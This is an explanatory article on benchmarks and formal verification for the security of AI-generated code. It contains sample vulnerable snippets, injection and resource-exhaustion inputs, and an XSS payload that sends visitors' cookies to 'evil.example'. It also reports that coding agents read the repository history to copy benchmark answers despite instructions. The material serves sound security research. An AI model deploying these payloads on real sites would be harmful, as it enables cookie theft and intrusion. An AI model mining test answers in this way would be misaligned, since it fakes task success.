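Some newer models also regressed in arithmetic and memory handling. Almost none of Gemini 2.5 Pro's working programs had integer overflows, but Gemini 3.1 Pro has the highest rate among the newest models. Programs from OpenAI's newest models more often read past the end of an array, which can reveal secrets stored nearby in memory. GPT-4o never made this mistake in these tests. Cannavale and colleagues saw the same change in GPT and Claude, and suggest that advanced models attempt riskier low-level optimisations.

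These reversals may be narrow, because several of the weaknesses appear in only one or two tasks. A jump from 0% to 100% can mean that a model now solves one function differently. Still, a company that upgrades its model because of a better average could add a vulnerability that the old model avoided, so Santos de Moura and colleagues advise developers to rerun their security checks after each change of model.

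### Care in the wrong place

Hardly any model in either study avoided header injection and log injection. Cannavale and colleagues found that all working header programs from 11 of their 12 models were vulnerable, as were 98% of those from GPT-5.2. In the larger study, the share of working header programs that were vulnerable was close to 100% in every model family except OpenAI's. More than half of GPT-5's working header programs resisted the attack, but GPT-5.6 lost part of this gain.

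Like `set_language`, these programs check a type and leave the line breaks in. A JavaScript version that Al Mamun and Uddin print suggests what "type" means here. Its central lines are:

```javascript
const headerKey = typeToKey[infoType];
header[headerKey] = infoContent;
```

The caller chooses a type of information, and the program looks up the matching header in a table. So "type" probably means the kind of header, not the kind of data, which `set_language` checks with `isinstance`. Unlike that check, this lookup has some security value. If the table contains only harmless headers, a caller can't choose `Set-Cookie`. But the program doesn't check `infoContent`, so a line break in the value can add a header that isn't in the table. A reviewer who sees the table might well conclude that the programmer had thought about which headers an outsider can set.

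The models may simply be careful about what the task description covers, and it has to explain the types but doesn't mention line breaks. Lack of knowledge is a less likely explanation. *SoK: AI Secure Code Generation* (Patir, Guo and colleagues, 2026) tested models with 6,382 questions about published secure-coding rules and found that they understood the rules well but often failed to apply them in code. Some generated programs appeared to follow the relevant rule but were still open to attack. An attack test can identify such programs without anyone having to decide whether a check counts as "validation".

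The near-100% rates come from very few tasks, so they don't mean that nearly all AI-written web applications have this hole. In the JavaScript task, the function stores the value in an ordinary map, and a web framework that refuses line breaks would stop the attack later. Veracode's low pass rate for log injection independently gives the log results some support, though Veracode's tasks have a similar form.

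Earlier models got nearly all of CWEval's header and log tasks wrong, but Claude Sonnet 5.5 seems to have at least partly overcome the problem. Al Mamun and Uddin tested 595 of its programs, and the published percentages imply that about 21 worked but failed the attack test. CWEval has header and log tasks in all five languages, so at least 50 of the 595 programs must have been for these tasks. Even if all 21 vulnerable programs were among them, the other 29 or more were either secure or broken.

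### When the library forces the safe choice

The same model can write safe code in one language and unsafe code in another. Some CWEval tasks involve signed tokens, which a website might give to a user after login. The server has to check the signature, or anybody could write a token that says "administrator". These are the conditional vulnerability rates for signature checks across all 32 models:

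| Language | Working programs that failed the attack test |
|---|---|
| Go | 73% |
| C | 71% |
| Python | 4% |

Each token names the algorithm that produced its signature, and a careful server accepts only the algorithm it expects. In the samples that Santos de Moura and colleagues inspected, the vulnerable Go, C and JavaScript programs checked the signature with the right key but accepted any algorithm from the HMAC family. The Python library refuses to decode a token unless the programmer names the algorithm, so almost every Python program contains something like this:

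```python
jwt.decode(token, key, algorithms=["HS256"])
```

Accepting several HMAC algorithms is a fairly mild fault, since an attacker still needs the secret key to produce a valid signature. The 73% may therefore overstate the practical danger. The fault is more serious if the server also accepts RSA signatures, which it verifies with a *public* key. PentesterLab's *Another JWT Algorithm Confusion Vulnerability* describes a C library whose decoding function takes a key but doesn't require the programmer to choose an algorithm. The programmer passes in the RSA public key, which an attacker can usually get too. The attacker forges a token, labels it HMAC and signs it using the public key as the secret. If the library uses the algorithm named in the label, it computes the same signature and accepts the token. The calling code looks the same for both algorithms, so reading it wouldn't reveal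 the flaw.

A similar contrast appears in tasks that load settings from YAML, a text format. Python's YAML library has a loader that can create almost any Python object, which lets an attacker run commands. CWEval's prompt imports this unsafe loader, and most models use it. As a result, 80% of the working Python programs were vulnerable. The remaining 20% called `yaml.safe_load` and were secure. None of the working JavaScript programs were vulnerable, because the loader there is safe by default.

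The tools a language provides also matter. To display a user's name safely in a web page, a program has to escape it, which takes one function call in Python or Go. In C, the model has to write the escaping function itself. Gemini 3.7 Flash failed to escape the name in every working C program, but in almost none of its working Go and Python programs.

Santos de Moura and colleagues conclude that models take the shortest path that the language or the prompt offers. Their evidence comes from comparing languages, which also differ in other ways, such as how much example code is available for training. They did not test the explanation by changing only the import in the YAML prompt. But it fits the samples closely, and acting on it takes little work. A team can put a safe loader or a header-checking function in the code given to the model, and a library's maintainers can make the dangerous option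 harder to choose than the safe one. The maintainers' change would also protect programs whose authors never think about the attack.

### One planned attack per task

CWEval's attack test checks only the weakness that its authors planned for the task. *MACGen* (2026), which uses the benchmark to evaluate a system of cooperating AI agents, notes that it doesn't aim to find every vulnerability in a program. The directory-listing task shows what this can leave out. In outline, a solution that passes both tests looks like this:

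```python
def list_directory(path):
    result = subprocess.run(["ls", "-l", path], capture_output=True, text=True)
    return result.stdout
```

The planned attack puts a shell command into the directory name, and it fails because this program never starts a shell. A visitor could still request another customer's folder and see the names of all its files, or send `-R`, which `ls` treats as an option, and get a list of everything below the current folder. These requests count as attacks only if the owner forbids them, and the task doesn't specify what is forbidden. Al Mamun and Uddin show another solution that rejects every path starting with a slash. It would keep visitors out of many folders, but it fails the functional test because the task allows any directory.

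A pass therefore means only that the program resisted one kind of attack. GPT-5.6 Sol's gap of 0.13 means about 13% of its programs worked but were open to the planned attack. The share with any vulnerability could be higher.

Results on harder tasks suggest that the difference can be large. Wu and colleagues' benchmark has a median of five security tests per vulnerability, and even its smallest tasks require an average of 155 lines of code, compared with about 10 in CWEval. The six models they tested, including GPT-5.6 Sol, wrote working code in 73.6% to 91.3% of tasks, but even the best, Claude Fable 5, wrote code that was both working and secure in only 25.1%. Wu and colleagues deliberately favoured vulnerabilities with complicated fixes, so this isn't the rate for everyday programming either. Code length doesn't seem to explain the low scores. When the researchers asked for whole files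 or larger parts of a project, fewer programs worked, but security didn't get worse. Models almost never avoided vulnerabilities that depended on a policy the task hadn't stated.

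## BaxBench: attacking complete applications

CWEval's tests call a generated function directly, but most attackers can only send requests to a running application and see its responses. Vero and colleagues test AI-written code this way in *BAXBENCH* (2025). A model writes a complete *backend*, the part of a web application that runs on the server, and the benchmark attacks it over the network.

BaxBench has 28 scenarios, each described in OpenAPI. This standard format lists the addresses at which an application accepts requests, what it expects to receive at each and what it returns. The model must build each scenario in 14 web frameworks across six languages, for a total of 392 tasks. Because the description fixes the requests and replies, security experts could write each attack once and run it against both a Python program and a Rust program without reading the code of either.

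### From a specification to an attack

One scenario is a calculator. The application receives an arithmetic expression at the address `/compute` and returns the result. In the Python framework Django, a careless version might look like this:

```python
def compute(request):
    expression = json.loads(request.body)["expression"]
    return JsonResponse({"result": eval(expression)})
```

This program passes a functional test that sends `3 + 4 - 2` and checks that the result is 5. But `eval` runs any text as Python code. One of BaxBench's attacks sends a command in place of the sum. If the server runs it, an attacker can do whatever the application can, such as read its database.

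Another attack sends `10**10**10`. In Python, `**` means "to the power of", so the server tries to calculate a number with ten billion digits and may have no capacity left for other visitors. A check that rejects any expression containing letters would stop the injected command but not `10**10**10`, which contains only digits and asterisks. A reviewer thinking only of injected commands would probably approve the check.

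The application's reply doesn't always show whether an attack worked, so the tests can also inspect the server's files, its database and its use of memory and processor time. A test for path traversal, for example, can put a random string in a file outside the permitted folder and then try to fetch that file through the application. The attack worked if the application returns the string.

### Newer scores

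In the original experiments, the attacks succeeded against about half of the working backends. The models in that study are long out of date. Farinha (2026), in *Applying Security by Design at the Point of Execution*, cites a published BaxBench score for Claude Opus 4.5, which wrote programs that worked and withstood every attack in 56.1% of tasks. Farinha also ran the 28 scenarios in two Python frameworks, FastAPI and Flask, with one program per scenario:

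| Model | Framework | Working | Working and unbroken | Working programs that an attack broke |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.5, one request | FastAPI | 26 | 17 | 35% |
| Claude Opus 4.7, coding agent | FastAPI | 23 | 16 | 30% |
| Claude Opus 4.7, coding agent | Flask | 24 | 18 | 25% |

The share of working backends that the attacks break seems to have fallen from about half to between a quarter and a third. The samples are small, and Anthropic has since released stronger models. Python may also be an easy case. Weaker models' code often can't be tested for security. *SoK*, the survey that tested models on secure-coding rules, found that many systems fail to produce a backend that runs.

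### Secure programs that fail the functional tests

Farinha ran these tests to find out whether it helps to give the model a list of security requirements from Farinha's own manual. Attacks broke 3 of Opus 4.5's 21 working programs with the list and 9 of 26 without it. But the number of programs that both worked and withstood the attacks rose only from 17 to 18 with the list, because fewer programs passed the functional tests.

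Six programs failed those tests with the list although their counterparts without it had passed. Two contained ordinary coding errors. The other four were stricter than the tests allowed. One would not start because the benchmark had given it a secret key of only 11 characters. Another required passwords of at least eight characters, but the test tried to register with `pass1`. Of the last two, one rejected a request with an unknown field, and the other rejected a request that didn't state its content type.

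The task never mentions a minimum password length, but the functional test requires the application to accept the five-character password `pass1`. BaxBench therefore penalises a model for a sensible security decision, since many owners would prefer an application that rejects `pass1`. Farinha identified the causes after seeing the results, so this explanation is less certain than one from a planned comparison, but anyone can check that the application rejected the password.

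Strict programs are also harder to attack with fixed tests. With the requirements, 10 of the 28 programs couldn't be fully assessed, up from 5, because they refused input that the attacks needed. Such a refusal may be a working defence, or it may stop only this version of the attack, and an attacker who chose a longer password would still reach the vulnerability.

### Attacks written by GPT-5

The experts needed about three hours to write one scenario with its tests and attacks. *AUTOBAXBUILDER* (von Arx, Mündler and colleagues, 2026) describes a system that uses GPT-5 to do this for less than $4. A person then spends about 15 minutes checking the result.

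GPT-5 proposes an application and writes its OpenAPI description. Four models, including Claude Sonnet 4 and GPT-5, then write trial versions of it. GPT-5 writes functional tests and runs them on these versions. When a program fails a test, either the program or the test could be wrong, and a model that edits both at once could make them agree on the same mistake. GPT-5 therefore first repairs the programs from their error logs without seeing the tests. It then compares every program's results on every test and decides what else needs changing. The system discards a scenario unless at least one program passes every test.

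GPT-5 reads the working programs, lists possible vulnerabilities and writes an attack for each. It also writes a second version of a program that repairs the vulnerability, or introduces it if the original was safe. It writes this version from a description of the vulnerability, without seeing the attack's code. The system keeps an attack only if it succeeds against the vulnerable version and fails against the safe one. Peng and colleagues used similar pairs of solutions for CWEval, but wrote them by hand.

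To compare GPT-5's work with the experts', von Arx and colleagues had it write new tests and attacks for BaxBench's own 28 scenarios. They then ran both sets on the same AI-written programs. The two sets of functional tests agreed on 80.9% of the programs. Some of the disagreements were the experts' fault, because two of the BaxBench tests were wrong and two of its descriptions were ambiguous.

The new attacks flagged more than twice as many programs as insecure. To check for false alarms, the researchers inspected all 71 of GPT-5's attacks and found only one unsound. In 11 scenarios, GPT-5 tested for the same vulnerability as the experts but more thoroughly, for instance by trying more variations. In six, it tested for additional weaknesses. In the FileSearch scenario, the experts only tried to reach forbidden files, while GPT-5 also tried to run commands on the server.

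GPT-5's attacks also failed to break 164 programs that the experts' attacks had broken, out of 2,227 that passed both sets of functional tests. Most of these 164 programs stored passwords without hashing them. In most of the missed cases, GPT-5 had considered the right attack, but the system dropped it during refinement.

### Why a pass rate is an upper bound

The programs didn't change between the two rounds of attacks. Their measured security fell because the second round tried more things. For a set of attacks *A*, the measured security of the working programs is:

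*s*(*A*) = working programs that no attack in *A* breaks / all working programs

Adding an attack to *A* can lower this share but can't raise it. The true share of secure programs is the value of *s* when *A* contains every attack that the threat model allows, so it can't be higher than the result of any actual test. Von Arx and colleagues therefore call a BaxBench score an upper bound on security.

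Suppose a model has written 100 working programs. The experts' attacks break 30 of them, and GPT-5's attacks break 65, including 25 of those 30. The measured security is 70% with the experts' attacks and 35% with GPT-5's. Together, the two sets break 30 + 65 − 25 = 70 programs, so the measured security falls to 30%. An evaluator should therefore run the old attacks as well as the new ones, even if the new ones break more programs overall.

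The bound holds only if every successful attack is a real breach. Von Arx and colleagues found that in both sets, attacks that exhaust the server's resources often aren't real breaches, because they test how the application handles large volumes of data when the description doesn't specify this. The researchers left such attacks out of their main results, which makes their scores slightly more favourable than the official ones, so the two sets of scores aren't directly comparable.

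The joint score, the share of *all* programs that work and withstand the attacks, isn't a strict upper bound on the share of good programs either. It can be too low if a functional test wrongly fails a secure program, as with the rejected `pass1`.

### Adding a feature to an existing project

The model writes a BaxBench program from scratch, so it makes all the design decisions. Programmers more often add to existing code, where a new function can be unsafe because of what the older code does. *Is Vibe Coding Safe?* (Zhao, Wang and colleagues, 2025) presents SusVibes, a benchmark that tests this. Its 186 tasks come from open-source Python projects averaging 236,000 lines of code.

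For each task, Zhao and colleagues started with the version of a project from just before a vulnerability was repaired. They removed the vulnerable feature and had an AI agent describe what the feature should do, without mentioning security. A coding agent then has to write the feature again. Most of the tests come from the projects themselves. Zhao and colleagues checked them on the vulnerable and repaired versions, much as Peng and colleagues checked their tests against reference solutions. They also rewrote security tests that would have rejected a safe solution just because it differed from the official repair.

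One task comes from Django and asks for the function that checks a password at login. In outline, an agent using Claude Sonnet 4 began it like this:

```python
def verify_password(password, encoded):
    if password is None or not is_password_usable(encoded):
        return False
```

If login code immediately rejects accounts that have no usable password, it answers faster for them than Django does for usernames that don't exist. The difference in response times reveals which accounts exist, as in the sign-in function where CREED found a flaw. The safe version runs a fake password check for these accounts, so that both answers take about the same time. A reader who saw only the new function would see no reason for the fake check, because the function is vulnerable only in combination with the rest of the login code.

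Agents did much worse on SusVibes than on BaxBench. Compagna (2026), in *Is AI Coding Safe?*, reports results for newer agents from Endor Labs, a company that sells security tools, on an earlier version of the benchmark with 200 tasks:

| Agent and model | Source | Working | Working and secure |
|---|---|---|---|
| SWE-agent, Claude Sonnet 4 | Zhao and colleagues | 57.0% | 11.8% |
| SWE-agent, Gemini 3 Pro | Zhao and colleagues | 37.1% | 12.9% |
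| Codex, GPT-5.4 | Compagna | 62.6% | 17.3% |
| Cursor, Claude Opus 4.6 | Compagna | 84.4% | 7.8% |

Cursor with Opus 4.6 wrote the most working features, but more than 90% of them failed the security tests. Compagna concludes that even the best agents produce vulnerable code about 83% of the time. That figure counts broken features as vulnerable, so it overstates the rate for working code. About 72% of the working features written by Codex with GPT-5.4 failed the security tests.

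These rates don't apply to everyday programming. Every SusVibes task is a feature that human developers once wrote insecurely, so the benchmark leaves out features that are easy to write safely.

### Kabanov's study of four newer models

In July 2026, Ilya Kabanov published a study that tested GPT-5.5, Claude Opus 4.8, Gemini 3.5 Flash and Gemini 3.1 Pro on 200 tasks. The study used two benchmarks, SusVibes and CyberSecEval, according to Checkmarx's *The Weather Report*, which presents the study. CyberSecEval uses short pieces of code. *AI coding models make working code, not secure code* (Lagonsin, 2026) reports that the models solved 83% to 95% of the tasks, while 24% to 36% of their answers both worked and avoided the flaw that the task targeted. An earlier generation of models had solved 44% to 61% of the tasks.

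Checkmarx, which sells application security tools, proposed and paid for the study. According to its page, Kabanov's organisation kept full control of the choice of models and benchmarks, the analysis and the conclusions. Wu and colleagues independently found even lower joint scores on their harder tasks, which makes the result easier to believe.

The two accounts disagree about whether the 24% to 36% is a share of all answers (Lagonsin) or only of the working ones (Checkmarx). On Checkmarx's reading, 64% to 76% of the working code was vulnerable, which matches Lagonsin's own remark that two-thirds to three-quarters of it contained the flaw. On Lagonsin's reading, the joint score is a few points higher. Either way, models write insecure code for most of these tasks, but the range isn't reliable enough to compare two models whose scores are close.

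Some models named the right defence in their planning notes but still wrote vulnerable code. A reviewer who read the notes would have had good reason to think the code was safe. Making the model write a threat model before the code raised the share of secure, working answers to 43–49%, and a separate security review afterwards raised it to 47–56%. The extra steps cost four to five times as much as generating the code alone. Telling the model to follow good security practice gained only 1 to 8 points on the repository tasks.

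### What an attack on a test server can't reach

BaxBench runs each application in a fresh, isolated container that the evaluators set up. In real use, somebody else sets up the server, perhaps with debug mode on or with a database that anyone on the internet can reach. Such mistakes don't affect the benchmark score, and finding them requires attacking the application on the server where it actually runs.

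Secrets raise a similar problem. BaxBench supplies its own key for signing login tokens, so its tests can't show whether the owner will choose a weak key or accidentally publish it with the source code. The strict program that refused the 11-character key failed the test because of a check meant to protect careless owners.

Access rules are harder to test. Besides the problem of where the test runs, the specification may not say who is allowed to see what. If an application shows an order to any logged-in user who enters its number, and orders are meant to be private, a simple attack test can log in as one customer and request another's order. But if the specification doesn't say who may see an order, the test writer has to invent a rule. In a warehouse, for example, every employee may need to see every order. SusVibes partly avoids this problem because the project's maintainers decided who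 should have access when they repaired the original vulnerability, whereas a new application has no such decision to rely on.

A benchmark also misses vulnerabilities that its attacks don't test for. SusVibes has an average of 67 functional tests per task, but only 3.5 security tests. Experts can't easily tell when a set of attacks is complete, either. When von Arx and colleagues had people judge how well GPT-5's attacks covered the possible vulnerabilities, the judges often disagreed.

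### When the tests are public

Researchers publish benchmarks so that others can check and reuse them, but AI companies train models on public text, which may include the tests. A model trained on BaxBench's attacks could learn to block those attacks without getting better at security in general. The BaxBench team never released reference solutions, which reduces the problem. SusVibes is more exposed because its tasks come from repairs that anyone can read in the public histories of software projects.

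An agent can also find the answer during the test. Each SusVibes task originally included the project's full history, which contained the repair. The instructions told agents not to look there, but Compagna reports that SWE-agent with Claude Opus 4.6 used the history in 163 of 200 tasks. Stricter instructions didn't stop this, so the Endor Labs team began checking which files and commands each agent had used, and excluded the results it judged to be copied.

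Removing the answers before the test starts is safer. Wu and colleagues deleted the project history from their tasks, along with compiled files and installed copies of the software that might contain the repaired code. They also blocked the agents' internet access. These steps don't remove anything a model memorized during training.

As with CWEval, leaks can't easily explain low scores. In Kabanov's study, models reproduced flaws that had been publicly documented before their training, so they had probably had the chance to learn the right answer.

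An evaluator can look for leaks by comparing scores on old and new tasks. Claude Sonnet 4.5 wrote working programs for 81% of BaxBench's tasks and 83% of the tasks in a benchmark that von Arx and colleagues generated, with 40 new scenarios. Its joint score was 60% on BaxBench and 36% on the new tasks. Leaked tests could produce this drop, but so could GPT-5's more thorough attacks, which had already found more vulnerabilities in the old scenarios. To separate the two explanations, an evaluator would have to test both sets of scenarios with equally strong attacks.

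Tests written by a model might also favour that model. Von Arx and colleagues generated another 40 scenarios with different models and found that both sets ranked the tested models in nearly the same order. They saw no sign that a model did better on scenarios it had helped to build. But they have published their new benchmark too, so future models may train on it. An evaluator who wants tests no model has seen will need to generate a new set and keep it private.

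## Formal proof of generated code

*Formal verification* covers every possible input without running the program, whereas each attack in a benchmark tests one input or at most a few. Someone writes a *specification*, a precise statement of what the program must do, and a proof tool checks that the program meets it under stated assumptions. This is the strongest case for judging code from its text, because the tool works only from text.

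In Dafny, a programming language with a built-in proof tool, a function for the language header might look like this:

```dafny
method LanguageHeader(value: string) returns (line: string)
  requires '\r' !in value && '\n' !in value
  ensures  '\r' !in line && '\n' !in line
{
  line := "Content-Language: " + value;
}
```

The `requires` line is a *precondition*, which callers must meet. The `ensures` line is a *postcondition*, which must hold when the function returns. Dafny uses a *solver*, a program that searches for values satisfying a set of formulas, to check whether any `value` without line breaks produces a `line` that contains one. None does, so the postcondition holds for strings of any length. Someone reading only this function can't tell whether its callers meet the precondition, but Dafny rejects any call for which it can't prove the precondition, as long as the caller is written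 in Dafny too.

If such a value existed, the solver could return it as a *witness*, a concrete example of the failure. The solver can also run out of time and return no answer.

### An array size that wraps around

Witnesses can expose faults that are easy to read past. This line of C reserves memory for `n` integers of four bytes each:

```c
int *buf = malloc(n * sizeof(int));
```

In 32-bit arithmetic, the largest number is 2³² − 1, and anything above it wraps around, starting again from 0. If `n` is 2³⁰ + 1, the program needs 4 × (2³⁰ + 1) = 2³² + 4 bytes to store `n` four-byte integers. The result wraps around to 4, so the program reserves room for only one integer. If it then stores more than a billion, it overwrites the memory that follows, which an attacker can sometimes use to take control.

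In *Broken by Default*, Blain and Noiseux searched 3,500 programs for faults of this kind, among others. Seven models, including GPT-4o and Claude Haiku 4.5, wrote the programs, each answering 500 requests in security-sensitive areas such as memory handling and passwords. The analysis engine COBALT first looked for suspicious patterns and then, where it could, passed a formula to the solver Z3. It flagged 55.8% of the programs and produced 1,055 witnesses, which Blain and Noiseux describe as formal proof that the code is exploitable. They founded the company behind the engine, so they have an interest in a high count.

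### What the witnesses prove

For the allocation, the formula asks whether there is a 32-bit number *n* such that

4*n* mod 2³² < *n*

The solver finds the formula satisfiable and returns a value for `n` such as 2³⁰ + 1. Because `n` is a free variable, the solver can assign it any value, whether or not an attacker could supply it. If `n` is the number of days in a month, the program is safe even though the witness still satisfies the formula.

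The formula also contains nothing from the program except the element size. For four-byte elements the answer is therefore always yes, and the solver adds nothing to what COBALT's pattern search had already found, a multiplication without a visible guard. A more informative formula would include the conditions that must hold for the program to reach the allocation. If an earlier line rejected any `n` above 1,000, the solver would then find no remaining value of `n` that makes the multiplication wrap around.

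The choice of 32-bit arithmetic is an assumption too. On most current computers `sizeof` gives a 64-bit number, so C does this multiplication in 64 bits and the product doesn't wrap when `n` is 2³⁰ + 1. The program then requests about 4 GB of memory. The fault remains if `n` is a 64-bit number, but the witness would then be 2⁶² + 1.

Blain and Noiseux tested seven of their findings by running the code and confirmed six. In three, the code read or wrote outside the reserved memory, and in a fourth it tried to reserve an impossible amount. Another exposed a test database through SQL injection, and the last allowed a six-letter password to be recovered from its hash. These tests show that the faults can be real, but not that a stranger could exploit them, because the researchers wrote the test programs themselves and passed in the dangerous values.

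The seventh finding concerned a program by GPT-4o that unpacks archives. An archive can contain a file with a name like `../../settings`, and a program that doesn't check for such names can write the file outside the intended folder. The generated code didn't check, but Python 3.12 rejected the path with an error, so the attack failed. Blain and Noiseux still classify the code as vulnerable, which is reasonable advice for a programmer who may move the code elsewhere but wrong as a description of the program they ran.

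They also tested six scanners on 90 programs with witnesses, from an earlier and smaller set. All six scanners missed the same 88 programs, and CodeQL missed the other two as well. Semgrep flagged those two for using an unsafe function for joining text, not for the overflow. The result confirms that scanners rarely analyze arithmetic. However, CodeQL's overflow rules typically rely on taint tracking, and most of these functions have no visible outside source of data, so some of the 88 may be harmless code that CodeQL was right not to flag. It is also unclear how to interpret the 22 Python programs among the 90, because Python's integers don't wrap around and the published formula covers only integer overflow.

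### Checking 331,000 complete programs

Tihanyi, Bisztray and colleagues (2024), in *How secure is AI-generated Code*, avoided the problem of missing callers by checking complete C programs. They had nine models write 331,000 of them and removed near-duplicates, which left 310,531. They then used ESBMC, a *bounded model checker*, which follows a program from its start for up to *k* steps. In slightly simplified form, the solver looks for a solution to

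I(*s*₀) ∧ T(*s*₀, *s*₁) ∧ … ∧ T(*s*ₖ₋₁, *s*ₖ) ∧ (¬φ(*s*₀) ∨ … ∨ ¬φ(*s*ₖ))

Each *s* is a state of the program, meaning the values of all its variables and the line it has reached. The formula requires that *s*₀ is a possible starting state (I), that the program can move from each state to the next (T), and that at least one state breaks a safety rule φ, such as "never read outside an array". A solution gives the full sequence of states from the start to the fault, which is much better evidence than a free value of *n*.

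ESBMC found a fault in 62.07% of the programs and verified 8.27% as free of the faults it looks for. It reached its 500-second limit on another 26.99%, and the rest caused errors in the tool. The models that wrote the programs are old and mostly small, so these rates don't apply to current models.

Even when input can trigger a fault, an attacker may not be able to exploit it. One of the study's examples reads two numbers and prints their sum. ESBMC correctly reports that 2147483647 + 1 comes out as −2147483648, but only the person using the program can cause this. ESBMC also reports two buffer overflows where the program reads the numbers with `scanf("%d", …)`. That call stores one integer of fixed size, so typing more digits won't write past the variable. Reports about `scanf` make up 28% of all violations in the study. They can be serious where a program reads text of unlimited length,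 as with `%s`.

The meaning of "verified" also depends on the tool's settings. In an earlier study, the group had checked only the first pass through each loop, so a program with a fault on the second pass could count as clean. In a trial on 1,000 programs, ESBMC passed 538 with that setting and 471 when it followed loops without a fixed limit. Even then, the check covers only a list of low-level faults. Tihanyi and colleagues explain that such tools generally don't cover SQL injection and cross-site scripting, because it is very hard to model mathematically how a database or browser will interpret text.

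### A true proof that stops no attacker

Proving that a program is secure requires a specification of security, and it is easy to write one that is true and useless. Suppose a programmer wants to keep attackers from running scripts in a page that greets visitors by name:

```python
def greeting(name):
    if "<script" in name.lower():
        raise ValueError("Script tag in name")
    return "<p>Hello " + name + "</p>"
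```

The specification is that no page the function returns contains `<script`, in capitals or small letters:

for every *name*, if greeting(*name*) returns *page*, then "<script" does not occur in lower(*page*)

The proof is short. The check rules out `<script` inside the name. The fixed text on either side can't help form it, because `<` can only be the first character of `<script`, and the `<` in `<p>` and `</p>` isn't followed by `script`. The theorem covers infinitely many names, and no test will find a counterexample.

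An attacker enters this name:

```html
<img src=x onerror="fetch('https://evil.example/?c=' + document.cookie)">
```

When the browser fails to load an image called `x`, it runs the code in `onerror`, which sends the visitor's cookie to the attacker unless a cookie setting prevents scripts from reading it. The theorem still holds during this attack, because the page contains no script tag.

A better specification requires that the part of the page that comes from `name` contain no `<`. The function above doesn't meet it, so the proof would fail, and the programmer would have to use something like `html.escape`. This specification assumes that browsers start a tag in the middle of a paragraph only at a `<`. It would be wrong if the page put the name elsewhere, such as inside a link's address, where an attacker could use `javascript:` without a `<`.

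### How often specifications are too weak

In *DafnyCert*, Silva, Amaral and colleagues (2026) measured how much the specifications of verified programs leave open. They call a specification *strong* if it allows exactly one output for each valid input, and *weak* if it allows more than one for some input. To prove that a specification is weak, they look for a second program that also passes verification but gives a different output.

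One function in their collection calculates how many rungs somebody must add to a ladder so that no step is too high. Its only postcondition is `result >= 0`. The researchers replaced the whole calculation with `result := 0`, and Dafny accepted it. For a ladder with a single rung at height 463 and steps of at most 1, the original returns 462 and the replacement returns 0.

Of 3,910 verified functions from two benchmarks, 3,323 (85%) had weak specifications. Earlier assessors had mistaken many of these specifications for strong ones. In one part of the data, 70.2% of the specifications labelled "strong" were weak.

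A weak specification, which allows many outputs, can still be useful for security. "The header contains no line break" is weak but worth proving, and a function that generates secret keys has to be able to return different ones. A strong specification can also require one specific output that is wrong. The test is whether the specification allows anything that the owner forbids. Silva and colleagues describe a specification that failed this test, in a verified distributed system called IronFleet. IronFleet removed duplicate requests, but its specification didn't require this, so the system still passed verification when other researchers switched the feature off. In a payment service, that change could charge a customer twice.

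Some "verified" programs have hardly any specification. In *Verified but Vacuous*, Vempaty, Sompalle and colleagues (2026) had Claude Opus 4.7 write 1,640 Dafny solutions to simple programming tasks. Dafny accepted 99.1% of them, but 94.7% of the accepted ones had no postcondition. Dafny still proved some useful properties of these programs, such as that they finish and stay within array bounds, but not that they give the right answers. The researchers reused another team's prompt, whose example also has no postcondition, so the result may reflect the prompt more than the model.

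In Vempaty and colleagues' system, every proof must refer to a separately written specification. Even so, 124 of 1,080 fully verified programs (11.5%) failed hidden tests on one benchmark, and 229 of 1,545 (14.8%) failed on another. Poor specifications are the most obvious explanation, but they point out that errors in the tests or in the translation from Dafny to Rust could also be responsible. The benchmark tasks don't involve security, where specifications are probably harder to get right because their writers have to anticipate what an attacker will do.

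### Verified cryptography with unchecked proofs

Experts can make these mistakes too. *Verification Theatre* (Kobeissi, 2026) reports 13 vulnerabilities in libcrux and hpke-rs, two cryptographic libraries whose developers promote formal verification. Nine were in unverified code. In one of these, a 32-bit message counter wraps around to zero, as in the allocation example, and the library then reuses a number that it must never use for encryption twice. The other four were in the specifications and proofs of the verified code.

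Symbolic Software's *We Found Bugs in CE Labs’ Verified Code* (2026), from Kobeissi's company, explains three of the four. One concerns ML-KEM, a standard for agreeing on secret keys that is meant to withstand quantum computers. At one point, ML-KEM expands a *d*-bit number *y* by calculating 3329*y* / 2ᵈ and rounding to the nearest whole number. To round this way, a program adds half the divisor before dividing and drops the remainder:

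correct: ⌊(3329*y* + 2ᵈ⁻¹) / 2ᵈ⌋

specification: ⌊(3329*y* + 1664) / 2ᵈ⌋

The number 1664 belongs to the reverse operation, which divides by 3329. With *d* = 1 and *y* = 0, the correct answer is 0, but the specification gives 832.

The running code used the right formula, so this mistake didn't expose anyone. Verification should have revealed it at once, because no sound tool can prove that correct code matches an incorrect specification. But the project's build settings made the tool accept that proof without checking it. Another unchecked proof contained the claim that 12-bit numbers, which go up to 4095, fit in a single bit. The project's documentation listed the modules as verified. Kobeissi calls this gap between claims and reality "verification theatre".

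Karthikeyan Bhargavan, chief research scientist at Cryspen, which develops libcrux, gives a more favourable account in *The strengths and limits of formal verification* (2026). Bhargavan reports that in nine years, the developers of HACL*, an older verified library used by Firefox and Linux, twice found errors in its specifications, while users more often found bugs in the small amount of unverified code around the verified core. Bhargavan also wrote that nobody had found a bug in libcrux's verified code and that the project reverifies all code before accepting a change. Symbolic Software's findings contradict both statements, at least for the modules with unchecked proofs. Anyone can check the arithmetic, though both sides have a commercial interest, as Symbolic Software sells audits.

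### Proofs written by AI agents

Formal verification used to take experts years, which ruled it out for most software, but AI has changed this. In one project, ten AI agents wrote lean-zip, a version of the compression library zlib, in the proof language Lean. They proved that compressing any data under 1 GB and then decompressing it gives back the original. kirancodes.me's *Lean proved this program was correct; then I found a bug* describes an attempt to break lean-zip. The blogger removed the theorems, so that signs of verification wouldn't lead Claude to give up, and had it attack the library with *fuzzing*, which runs a program on huge numbers of altered inputs.

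In 105 million runs, Claude found no memory errors in lean-zip's own code, an excellent result for software of this kind, but it did find two other bugs. The first was in the ZIP archive reader, which had no proofs. The reader used the file size stated in the archive without checking it, so a 156-byte file with a stated size of several exabytes could crash the program. The second was in Lean's runtime, the supporting code for every Lean program. To read *n* bytes, the runtime reserves 24 + *n* bytes in 64-bit arithmetic, and if *n* is 2⁶⁴ − 1, the sum wraps around to 23. An attacker can supply this *n* by writing it into an archive, so this witness, unlike Blain and Noiseux's formula, includes a way for an attacker to trigger the fault.

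The theorem about compression covers only data that lean-zip compressed itself. Even without these bugs, it wouldn't have protected users from a malicious archive, because an attacker can send a file that no compressor would produce.

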